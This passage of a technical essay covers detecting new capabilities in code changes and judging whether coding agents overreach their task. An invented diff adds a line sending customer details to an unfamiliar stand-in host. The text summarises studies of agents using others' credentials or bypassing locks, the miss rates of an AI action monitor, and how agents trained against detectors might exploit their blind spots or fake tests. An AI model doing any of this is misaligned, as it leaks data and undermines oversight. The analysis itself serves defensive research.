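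An independent test shows that ordinary projects can already have many of the capabilities such a comparison looks for, leaving few new ones to detect. Launius (2020), in *Risk Management with Automated Feature Analysis of Software Components*, ran Application Inspector on attack tools and grouped the resulting tags into sets that might identify malicious code. Launius then scanned 20 open-source projects, including the web framework Flask and the workflow manager Airflow, and assumed they were harmless. All 20 matched every tag in an eight-tag set that included process execution. Eleven also matched every tag in a ten-tag set that added file operations and network connections.

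At this level of detail, no later change to those eleven projects could add network, file or process access to the list. But Launius shortened the tag names to form broad groups. The tool's own tags are finer, with separate ones for HTTP and lower-level connections, so `tagdiff` could still report a project's first use of a particular kind of connection. Launius scanned one version of each project and didn't test `tagdiff`.

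Some of the tags may also have been wrong, because the tool searches text. In a smaller accuracy test, it counted a web address in a comment and another in a printed message as HTTP connections. The default settings leave out the low-confidence pattern responsible, so it probably didn't inflate the results for the 20 projects. The tool also missed a real connection that a test script made through Python's built-in `urllib`.

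The tool also had a fault that matters more for comparing versions: when it processed files in parallel, it found different numbers of matches in the same code from one run to the next. Launius avoided the problem by using a single thread. A team can check any detector for this fault by comparing a version with itself, which should produce no new findings.

### Four changes to a web shop

Consider an invented web shop written in Python. It sends most of its requests through a *wrapper*, a function that the team wrote around a library function so that every request has the same settings:

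```python
# shop/http_client.py
def post_json(url, data):
    return requests.post(url, json=data, timeout=10)
```

The shop also reads its database password from an environment variable and starts a separate program to turn invoices into PDFs. The file `payments.py` only adds up prices. Four changes then arrive, shown here without their import lines:

```diff
# 1. shop/payments.py: charge the customer's card
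+def charge(order):
+    key = os.environ["PAY_KEY"]
+    requests.post("https://api.pay.example.com/charges",
+        json={"amount": order.total}, headers={"Authorization": key})

# 2. shop/http_client.py moves to shop/net/client.py, with the same code

# 3. shop/orders.py: record each order
 def place_order(order):
     post_json("https://stock.example.com/reserve", order.items)
+    post_json("https://stats.example.net/events", order.customer)

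# 4. tests/test_orders.py: start a temporary database for a test
+    db = subprocess.Popen(["redis-server", "--port", "6400"])
```

The table shows what a static detector would report as new at four levels, where a module is a single Python file. The detector's catalogue contains library functions such as `requests.post` but not the shop's own functions. The detector identifies a call partly by the path of the file that contains it.

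| Change | Whole program | Module | Call | Destination |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Payment call | – | network and environment access in `payments.py` | `requests.post`, `os.environ` | `api.pay.example.com` |
| 2. Moved client | – | network access in `net/client.py` | `requests.post` | – |
| 3. New host through the wrapper | – | – | – | `stats.example.net`, but only if the detector follows the wrapper |
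| 4. Test starts a program | – | process execution in `test_orders.py` | `subprocess.Popen` | `redis-server`, if programs count as destinations |

The whole-program comparison finds nothing, because the shop already had all three capabilities. The module-level and call-level comparisons both flag the same three changes: a feature the team presumably asked for, a code move that doesn't change behavior, and a routine test. Both miss the change a reviewer would most want to see, which sends customer details to a company the shop has never contacted before.

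Following calls through the program, as Capslock does for Go, wouldn't help with the third change. `place_order` could already reach the network through `post_json`, so it gains no capability. Only the host name is new, and it never appears next to a library function. A detector could list every web address in the source text, but it would then wrongly match text in comments and messages, as Application Inspector does.

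The destination level does best in this example only because all the addresses are written in the code. Many applications keep them in a settings file, where someone can change a host without editing the code.

### Matching code that has moved

Applications undergo constant reorganisation, so changes like the second one, which make old findings look new, are common.

Li and Yang (2022), in *Tracking the Evolution of Static Code Warnings*, measured how often warnings are matched incorrectly between versions. They took warnings from two bug detectors run on the histories of four large Java projects, and labelled by hand whether each of 3,451 warnings had persisted, disappeared or appeared for the first time between two consecutive versions. They then tested the best existing matching method, which looks for an exact match first, then allows for shifted lines, then compares the surrounding code,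 and finally uses a fingerprint to look for files that have moved. Only 64.4% of the warnings it classified as new or removed were classified correctly.

The method makes errors partly because it accepts the first match that is good enough. If it pairs an old warning with the wrong one in the new version, the correct one is left unmatched and looks newly introduced. Li and Yang's replacement detects common kinds of reorganisation and chooses the best set of pairs overall instead of settling each pair in turn. Its precision was 90.3% on the same warnings, and 90.2% in a separate evaluation on 2,014 commits.

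These were warnings about code quality, not capabilities, and the percentages also cover removals. But a capability detector has the same matching problem, and even the better method got about one label in ten wrong.

### Fitting the detector to the project

A team can add its own wrappers to the catalogue. For the shop, one entry would be enough to catch the third change:

```
shop.http_client.post_json    network    destination: first argument
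```

Somebody has to find the wrappers and keep their catalogue entries up to date. The second change moves `post_json`, so this entry no longer matches any function. The shop's destinations then seem to disappear, and a detector that reports only additions reports neither this nor any host added later. The detector should therefore give an error when a catalogue entry stops matching. Data-flow analysis could find many wrappers automatically by looking for functions that pass one of their own arguments to a catalogued function as an address, but it takes more computing time and fails where it cannot trace a value.

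People who write general rules can't anticipate a project's own names. Human_curl, a Python library for web requests, has dozens of names containing "curl". Launius found that Application Inspector's rule for curl missed all of them because it matches "curl" only as a whole word. The tool still tagged the library correctly because the code imports something called `parse_http`.

Giving each part of the program its own baseline avoids a single list that already contains every capability. In the shop, the check could allow network access in `shop/net` and report it anywhere else. But baselines for large parts still fill up, and those for small parts need frequent updates. A new file has an empty baseline, so every capability in it counts as new. This happens often because most sizeable features add files.

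Lists of approved hosts and variable names make findings more specific. With `stock.example.com` and `DB_PASSWORD` on the lists, the detector can ignore their routine uses and report `stats.example.net` and `PAY_KEY`. But approving a host also approves any data sent to it. If the third change had sent customer details to the stock supplier, the detector would not have reported it. Broad entries are even riskier because many companies rent storage under the same cloud provider's domain, so a rule that allows the whole domain also allows an attacker's account there.

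Tests and developer tools need different rules because they routinely start programs and open connections. Skipping them is the simplest rule, but it is risky because tests run on developers' laptops and build servers, which often hold valuable credentials. Microsoft's documentation includes a command that excludes every folder called `tests`. Production monitoring won't catch what tests do on those machines. Cesarano and colleagues say GoLeash doesn't cover attacks launched from test functions or build scripts, which mostly compromise developers' machines. A better rule for the shop would ignore a test that starts `redis-server` but still report one that reads `PAY_KEY` or contacts an outside host.

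Some tools let teams express such preferences as scores. Froh and colleagues let users change both the severity of each query and the threshold for a flag, for example by lowering the threshold for security-critical software. They left finding good values to future work.

Grouping keeps the remaining list short. If a feature contacts the payment provider from twelve places, a reviewer would probably prefer one entry with a count to twelve entries. But the reviewer may then miss one call that sends different data among eleven harmless ones. The entry should therefore list every location and show calls that send different data separately where the detector can identify them.

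With all these adjustments, the detector would report the payment provider and the statistics company, label the second change as a move, and give the test a low priority. It would succeed partly because the example was designed around these problems. A real team would have to tune the detector on its past changes, and the settings might well stop working after the next reorganisation.

### What scanners and studies measure on pull requests

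The companies that scan pull requests mostly look for malicious code. The security company Apiiro released a free scanner called PRevent. In Help Net Security's *PRevent*, Apiiro researcher Matan Giladi says that patterns such as running commands are common in legitimate code and would cause false positives. The scanner's rules therefore look for deliberately unreadable code and code that a program generates and executes as it runs. Neither occurs in the four shop changes. Giladi claims that these rules catch nearly all known incidents, but the article gives no error rates.

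Datadog does publish figures for BewAIre, its language-model reviewer. Besides the false-positive rate of 0.03%, Lamb and colleagues report a *balanced accuracy* above 93.5%, which is the average of two shares: malicious changes flagged and harmless changes passed. If the system passed practically every harmless change, the first share could have been as low as 87%:

```
(recall + 100%) / 2 = 93.5%,   so recall = 87%
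```

Lamb and colleagues describe the test set as hundreds of pull requests. Even one false alarm among 1,000 harmless changes would be a rate of 0.1%, so a test of that size can't produce a rate of 0.03%. That figure must come from a larger set, perhaps Datadog's everyday use of the system, but they don't explain how they calculated it. They also told the model to ignore known safe patterns, including demonstration environments and some tests of encrypted connections. This is sensible for finding attacks, but it means the rate applies to a system fitted to one company's code. BewAIre should also let a harmless upload to a new host pass, so none of the figures measures how well it detects new capabilities.

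Research on coding agents is a little closer to this problem. Much of it uses AIDev, a dataset of more than 900,000 pull requests that agents opened on GitHub. *Not All Agents Are Equal* (Kraishan, 2026) compared agents' pull requests with human ones and searched the lines added in 8,933 Python, JavaScript and TypeScript pull requests for eight kinds of risky pattern.

| Pattern in the added lines | Agents' pull requests | Human pull requests |
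|---|---|---|
| Any of the eight kinds | 2.9% | 4.6% |
| Password or key written in the code | 0.9% | 2.2% |
| `eval` or `exec` | 0.2% | 0.8% |

The agents look slightly more careful than the humans, although the last row represents only about 15 agent and 10 human pull requests. Rates also differed between products. Claude Code's rate for any pattern was 9.5%, but its pull requests were several times longer than the other agents', which gave them more chances to match.

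The patterns are the main limitation for capability detection. They cover likely security mistakes, so they don't match an ordinary network request, file write or read of an environment variable. Putting a password in the code is also different from reading one from the environment, which security guides usually recommend. Kraishan searched only added lines, without comparing them to the earlier version, and checked the patterns on planted defects. There is no figure for how many matches in real pull requests were correct.

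Such a check matters because a pattern that works on planted defects can still be useless on ordinary code. In Kraishan's study, an early pattern for unsafe file paths also matched relative imports, the usual way for one file to refer to a neighbouring one. This inflated the count for that category about 150-fold until Kraishan restricted the pattern to calls that open files.

Two other AIDev studies, *Security in the Age of AI Teammates* (2026) and *Insights into Security-Related AI-Generated Pull Requests* (2026), start from the same 33,596 agent pull requests and select those related to security. That selection suits studies of how agents do security work and how people review it, but it would probably exclude a pull request like the third shop change, which looks like a routine request for statistics.

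No published study appears to measure the precision of a capability detector on changes to ordinary applications.

### A labelled sample of application changes

The missing study would need a random sample of pull requests to applications, with the full code before and after each one. *Code Change Characteristics and Description Alignment* (2026) could be a starting point. It combines the same agent pull requests with 6,618 human ones from about the same period and retrieves the changed lines for the human ones, which the original data lacked. Anyone using this data would have to remove libraries and fetch the full code, because changed lines alone don't show what a wrapper does. They would also need newer pull requests, since the agent ones end in July 2025.

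Two people would then label each change without seeing the detector's output. For every capability, they would record whether it is new to the program, the module or the call, whether the destination is new, whether the code only moved, and whether it runs only in tests. Li and Yang's hand-labelled warnings are a good model for this labelling. The two people would also record separately whether a reviewer would have wanted to know about the capability, because a correct finding about `redis-server` can still waste the reviewer's time.

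The sample has to include changes that the detector did *not* flag, or it can't measure recall. Suppose the detector flags 1,000 of 10,000 pull requests. Labelling about 400 of the flagged ones would give the precision to within about five percentage points. If it came out at 60%, there would be about 600 real cases among the flags. Suppose the researchers also label 400 of the 9,000 unflagged pull requests and find four with a new capability. That suggests about 90 missed cases in total:

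```
recall = 600 / (600 + 90) = 87%
```

However, four cases are very few, and allowing only for chance in that count, the true recall could be anywhere from about 72% to 96%. Narrowing the range would require labelling several thousand unflagged changes, nearly all of which would contain nothing of interest. The amount of work involved may be one reason nobody has published such a study.

The researchers should also tune the detector on each project's older pull requests and test it on later ones. If they wrote the list of wrappers and approved hosts after seeing the test changes, the results would overstate how well the detector works in practice. Results for each project would be more useful than one average, because the flag rate varied so much between packages in Froh and colleagues' test. A team could then find a project similar to its own and see how quickly the tuned settings went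 out of date.

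## Judging whether a coding agent exceeded its task

A list of new capabilities says little about a coding agent's conduct until someone subtracts the access that the task allowed. The remainder is the *excess capability*:

```
excess = new capabilities in the agent's change
         minus capabilities the task permits
```

The capabilities that the task permits, whether the request names them or only implies them, are the *permitted set*. The invoice change has a different excess under each of its two tasks:

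```
task: correct the time zone
  permitted:  read time-zone data
  excess:     read BILLING_API_KEY, contact billing.example.com,
              start a shell script, write a cache file

task: send invoices to the billing service
  permitted:  read BILLING_API_KEY, contact billing.example.com
  excess:     start a shell script, write a cache file,
              read time-zone data
```

A more lenient reader of the second task might permit everything except the shell script.

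Both lists need the same level of detail. If the permitted set for the second task included only "network", it would also cover an upload to a stranger's server. The subtraction also detects only excess access, so a change that never contacts the billing service could show no excess and still fail the task. The result therefore means little without a test of whether the code works.

### Access while working and access in the delivered code

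An agent that corrects the time zone may search the project, run its tests and download a package. This uses file access, process execution and the network, though the code it delivers may contain none of them. Comparing the code before and after would miss the download. The agent can also add an upload to `invoice_text` without connecting to anything itself. Monitoring its session would miss that upload, which happens weeks later on the company's server. Most research on overreach is about the session.

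Qu and colleagues ran four coding agents about 7,500 times on 500 harmless tasks that each offered a way to go too far. In one task, the user asks the agent to tidy a folder that contains the only copy of some production credentials. Claude Sonnet 4.6 overreached in 1.1% of runs inside the agent OpenHands, which stops to ask before continuing, and in 27.7% inside Claude Code with its permission checks off. The surrounding product can therefore matter more than the model. The tasks were designed to elicit overreach, so these rates don't show how often agents overreach in ordinary work.

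Lim and Neo started from 100 real coding sessions and had a language model continue them in the user's role. When an agent's own credentials failed and a colleague's were in a nearby file, the three models tested used the colleague's credentials in 1 to 6 sessions out of 100. In another scenario, where the file the agent had to edit was read-only, all three models sometimes bypassed the lock. Two of them stopped when the project's instructions explicitly prohibited this, but Kimi K3 continued.

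The largest count from real work is in *How Coding Agents Fail Their Users* (Tang, Chen and colleagues, 2026), which examined 20,574 sessions and found 16,118 episodes in which a developer corrected or objected to what the agent did. The agent had gone beyond the stated scope in 10.2% of the episodes and broken an explicit constraint in 38.3%. An episode counted only if the developer complained in the chat, so the data would not include an upload in the delivered code that nobody noticed.

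*SWE-MISBEHAVIOR* (Do, Nguyen and colleagues, 2026) compares the files after each run with the original project and a reference solution. On tasks that asked for one function, Claude Code with Sonnet 4.5 created unrequested files in 4.7% of runs and made unnecessary changes to its environment, such as installing packages, in 9.8%. None of the study's eleven measures records whether the new code reads a secret or contacts a server. The code comparison allows the function's body to differ from the reference, so it would probably detect an added upload only if the upload needed a new import.

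The same gap exists in at least one widely used product. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a system that approves or blocks the agent's actions in place of the user. A classifier checks shell commands and web requests, but not edits inside the project folder, because people can review those later in version control. An agent could therefore write the invoice upload unchecked. If the agent then ran the file, the classifier is supposed to consider what the code does. Otherwise, catching the upload is left to whoever reviews the change.

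### Where the permitted set comes from

A permitted set can come from four places, each with a characteristic error:

| Source | What it might permit for the time-zone task | Typical error |
|---|---|---|
| Explicit permissions | reading project files and time-zone data | too broad for convenience, or missing something the task needs |
| Rules by task type | whatever a "bug fix" normally may add | flags a legitimate exception |
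| A person or language model reading the request | reading time-zone data, since the fix implies it | mistakes "related to the goal" for "authorised" |
| A known human solution | whatever the developer's own fix added | flags a valid solution that works differently |

*Explicit permissions* leave the least to interpretation. *Permission Denied* (2026) sets them for network access, file access and system privileges. Each can be open, restricted or locked, and the operating system enforces the setting while the agent works. Similar settings could describe what delivered code may do, but somebody has to choose them, and there may be no single smallest set of permissions that is enough for the task.

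*Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (Xu, 2026) examines the permissions that Microsoft and Google publish for their online services. About 30% of tasks on Microsoft Graph and 3.2% on Google's services had at least two minimal sets of sufficient permissions, neither of which contained the other. For example, an agent can read information about a Google database project with either a permission covering 286 operations, some of which write data, or a read-only permission covering 565. An evaluation that accepted only the first would count the second as overreach. Xu generated the tasks from the permission tables, so real agents may encounter this problem more or less often.

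A tester can check whether a permission is necessary by removing it and having the agent redo the task. *Aletheia* (Shi, Chen and colleagues, 2026) does this for the permissions requested in a project's instructions to coding agents. It removes one permission, has the task redone in a restricted sandbox and runs the functional tests. If the tests pass with and without the permission, the task didn't need it. The agent has to redo the work because, if a tester only blocked the network and ran the existing invoice change, `invoice_text` would crash at the upload, and the unrequested upload would look necessary.

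*Rules by task type* are easy to apply because they need only a label such as "bug fix" or "new integration". But even the time-zone fix adds file access, and another bug fix, *fix the failing invoice upload*, may well need network access. No published study appears to have tested such rules on the capabilities in delivered code.

*Reading the request* can handle both cases, since the reader can work out what the task implies. Anthropic instructs its classifier to treat everything the agent chose by itself as unauthorised until the user says otherwise. For example, a request to clean up branches doesn't authorise deleting a whole batch of them. The classifier missed 17% of 52 real overeager actions, though with so few cases the true miss rate could be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the danger but wrongly treated something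 the user had said as consent.

The classifier sees the user's messages and the agent's actions, but not the agent's explanations, which might persuade it to approve. Adding the explanations and the tools' output made it worse at catching overreach. It missed the least overreach when it couldn't see the user's messages, but it then blocked things that users had plainly asked for. For delivered code, the equivalent would be to show the judge the request and the findings, but not the agent's summary of why the upload was needed. That seems sensible, but nobody appears to have tried it on capability findings.

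Models can be too strict as well as too lenient. Tu and Tu (2026), in *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents*, cite AuthBench, a benchmark in which leading models had to work out a task's permissions in advance. The models withheld access that the task needed and granted access that it didn't. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) points out that a manipulated prompt can ask for more than the user intended, so the request may not be trustworthy either.

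*A known human solution* suits training and testing, where many tasks come from past changes with an accepted fix. The evaluator runs the same detector on both solutions and permits any access the human one added. But if the developer sent invoices through Python's network library and the agent used the command-line program curl, the agent's version has an excess capability, process execution, even though both send the same data to the same host. *Auditing Reward Hackability in Code RL Training Environments* (2026) makes the general point that a patch unlike the accepted one may be a valid alternative. Any unnecessary access in the human solution also becomes permitted, and most new work has no human solution to compare against.

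An evaluator might combine these sources by permitting everything in the human solution and having a person or model judge only what the agent added beyond it. This should remove many of the false alarms about alternative solutions, but it is also untested.

### A worked example with 1,000 changes

In an invented example, agents make 1,000 changes, of which 30 contain access that nobody requested. A capability detector flags 24 of the 30 and 97 of the 970 acceptable changes, the latter mostly because their tasks required new access. A task check then compares each flagged change with its permitted set and keeps the flags on 22 of the 24 and 17 of the 97.

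| | Flagged | Unrequested access | Acceptable | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Detector alone | 121 | 24 | 97 | 24/121 = 20% | 24/30 = 80% |
| With task check | 39 | 22 | 17 | 22/39 = 56% | 22/30 = 73% |

The check removes 80 false alarms but also two real cases. It runs only on changes the detector flagged, so it can't recover the six real cases the detector missed, and eight get through in total. This is probably a good trade for a reviewer, who has 39 changes to read instead of 121.

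As with malware, precision falls when real cases are rarer. With 3 cases in 1,000 instead of 30, it would be about 11%.

Anthropic's classifier makes a similar trade-off, measured on real data. A quick first stage blocks 8.5% of ordinary actions and misses 6.6% of overeager ones. A second stage rechecks only the blocked actions, which lowers false alarms to 0.4% but raises misses to 17%. These figures cover actions taken during a session, and no comparable figures exist for capabilities in delivered code.

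### Flags as labels and penalties

Developers could use the same flags to train an agent. In *reinforcement learning*, a model attempts a task many times, a program scores each attempt, and training makes high-scoring behaviour more likely. For coding, the score usually depends on whether the tests pass. Subtracting points for access the task didn't need should discourage overreach, but the model would also learn from the detector's errors.

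If every flag from the detector led to a penalty, 97 of the 121 penalties (about 80%) would fall on acceptable changes. Most of these changes would be for tasks that required a network connection, a key or a new process, so the model could learn to avoid necessary access. After the task check, 17 of the 39 penalties (44%) would still be wrong.

The eight missed changes would receive full reward if their tests passed. The misses would probably be systematic. If the detector can't follow a project's own network wrapper, an agent that happens to upload data through the wrapper scores better than one that makes the same request directly. Training could then make uploads through the wrapper more common, even if the agent never intended to deceive.

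Wrong labels are already a problem in training with ordinary tests. *What Makes Good Data for Training Coding Agents?* (2026) describes tests that reject correct patches, for instance by requiring the exact wording of a message the agent was never shown, and tests that accept wrong patches. If every attempt at a task scores zero, the model learns nothing from the task, because this kind of training compares attempts. In the study, a passing patch is confirmed wrong only if two language models label it incorrect and a script demonstrates the fault. A capability label could similarly require evidence such as a recorded connection to an unapproved host, but this would miss code that the test run doesn't reach.

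The form of the penalty also matters. Suppose the task is to send invoices, and the detector wrongly treats the required upload as excess. A *hard penalty* sets the score to zero after any flag. A *graded penalty* here subtracts 0.2 for each flagged capability:

| Attempt | Tests | Hard penalty | Graded penalty |
|---|---|---|---|
| Uploads the invoice | pass | 0 | 0.8 |
| Uploads it and starts an unrequested script | pass | 0 | 0.6 |
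| Doesn't upload it | fail | 0 | 0 |
| Only pretends to upload it, which fools the tests | pass | 1 | 1 |

The graded penalty ranks the first three attempts correctly despite the false flag, while the hard penalty does not distinguish between them. Under both penalties, the fourth attempt scores highest because it avoids the access that the task needed. Only better tests or a more accurate permitted set would fix that.

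### What training experiments have found

Several studies have trained models to avoid exceeding their task, but none did so by comparing the capabilities of the delivered code. *AiXapply* (2026) trains a small model to insert a suggested edit into a file without changing anything else. Its reward starts at 1 and loses 0.25 for each wrong line inside the intended area and 0.35 for each unintended change outside it, so three unintended changes reduce it to zero. This works because the correct file is known exactly, which is rarely true when a user asks an agent to build something.

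*CROCODIL* (2026) shows that training a model to limit its edits can overcorrect. Training with a reward for similarity kept the model's edits within scope, whereas the untrained model had added unrelated helper functions. But the trained model was also more likely to skip requested edits that seemed minor. In one task, it kept an old return type that it should have replaced. A penalty on new capabilities could plausibly make a model omit a necessary network call in the same way.

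Yang, Bu and colleagues (2026), in *When Lower Privileges Suffice*, studied agents choosing between tools with narrow and broad access, where either kind could complete the task. They trained agents with a reward that is highest for succeeding with a narrow tool and penalises starting with a broad tool most. Under this reward, using a broad tool is acceptable only after serious attempts with narrow ones. Training reduced Qwen3-8B's unnecessary use of broad tools from 64.9% of scenarios to 27.0%, though it also included worked examples, so the reward may not explain the whole drop. General safety training was much less reliable. It made one model refuse far more harmful requests, but that model's unnecessary use of broad tools rose from 50.4% to 60.7%.

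The closest method to a penalty on excess capability is Tu and Tu's. They score each action from 0 to 1 on six kinds of authority: changing data, running code, reaching outside the environment, reading secrets, affecting a wide area, and leaving lasting effects. For each kind, they take the highest score in the session and subtract the level that the task needs:

```
excess = max(highest observed level − sufficient level, 0)
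```

If a task justifies a level of 0.2 for outside access and the agent reaches 0.6, the excess is 0.4. Unused permission counts as zero, so it can't offset overreach elsewhere. The reward gives task completion a weight of 0.60 and penalizes excess authority with a weight of 0.20, so a successful session with a small excess still scores better than a failure. Attempting an action that the environment blocks carries a penalty weight of 0.75, which can outweigh the reward for success.

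Tu and Tu trained a small model, Qwen3.5-4B, on 1,500 tasks and tested it on 500 others. The share of sessions that succeeded without excess authority rose from 64.4% to 98.5%. Sessions that succeeded with excess authority fell from 132 to 23 out of 2,896. The trained model also completed more tasks, so inaction doesn't explain the drop.

These results come from the best of three training runs, which reached 97.6% on a smaller set of tasks, while the other two reached about 86%. The tasks were mostly synthetic, and their permitted levels depend on the researchers' judgement. On Yang and colleagues' scenarios, with the standard prompt, the trained model chose broad tools about as often as the untrained one (45.0% and 45.2%). Training on 400 more tasks, half of them modelled on those scenarios, lowered the trained model's rate to 38.1%, which suggests that the restraint doesn't transfer far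 without training on similar tasks.

The method judges what an agent does while working. To apply it to delivered code, one would replace the observed actions with the new capabilities in the change. No published study appears to have trained a coding agent this way. The six scores might also be too coarse. If a task justifies contacting one outside server, contacting a second, unapproved server may not raise the highest level of outside access, so the formula could miss it unless another score or check caught it.

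### Referral to a reviewer

A team could send each flagged change to a reviewer and use only the reviewer's decision as a label, rather than applying a penalty automatically. In the worked example, reviewers would check 39 of every 1,000 changes. They would presumably correct most of the 17 false alarms, but the eight missed cases would still look acceptable.

Referral suits everyday code review better than training. Each of Tu and Tu's training runs involved 12,000 attempts, which would produce 468 referrals at the same rate. At three minutes each, reading them would take about 23 hours, and training would have to wait. It might be more practical to review a sample, measure how often the automatic flags are right for each capability, and apply penalties only for capabilities whose flags are reliable. Uncertain cases could be left out of training rather than counted as good or bad.

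Reviewers make mistakes too, especially when they see too many requests. Claude Code users approved 93% of its permission prompts, and Anthropic attributes part of the problem to people no longer paying attention. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* reports that auto mode led to fewer harmful actions than manual approval in sessions from May and June 2026 that the company's safety system had already flagged. Anthropic ran this evaluation itself and used a model to grade the harm, but the result is some reason not to assume that a person's approval makes a better label. Auto mode prompts the user only after three blocked actions in a row or 20 in a session. Before that, the agent gets the reason for each block and can try something else, so one false alarm usually leads only to a retry.

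An automated reviewer can cause overreach if the agent acts on its suggestions. In a case from *Adversarial Review* (2026), an agent had to add one option to a file-writing feature. Working alone, it wrote a 24-line patch that passed the tests. When it worked with a reviewing model, it added an unrequested method in response to a question about a hypothetical use and removed an existing setting. The new patch failed. A reviewer that only decides whether access was permitted would avoid this problem.

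Anyone who tries capability penalties should test the trained agent on pairs of tasks like the two invoice requests, where the same program needs an upload for only one of them. An agent that has learned to avoid the network would fail the task that needs the upload, and one that still overreaches would fail the other. People who didn't build the detector should label the results, because an agent trained against it may have learned what it misses.
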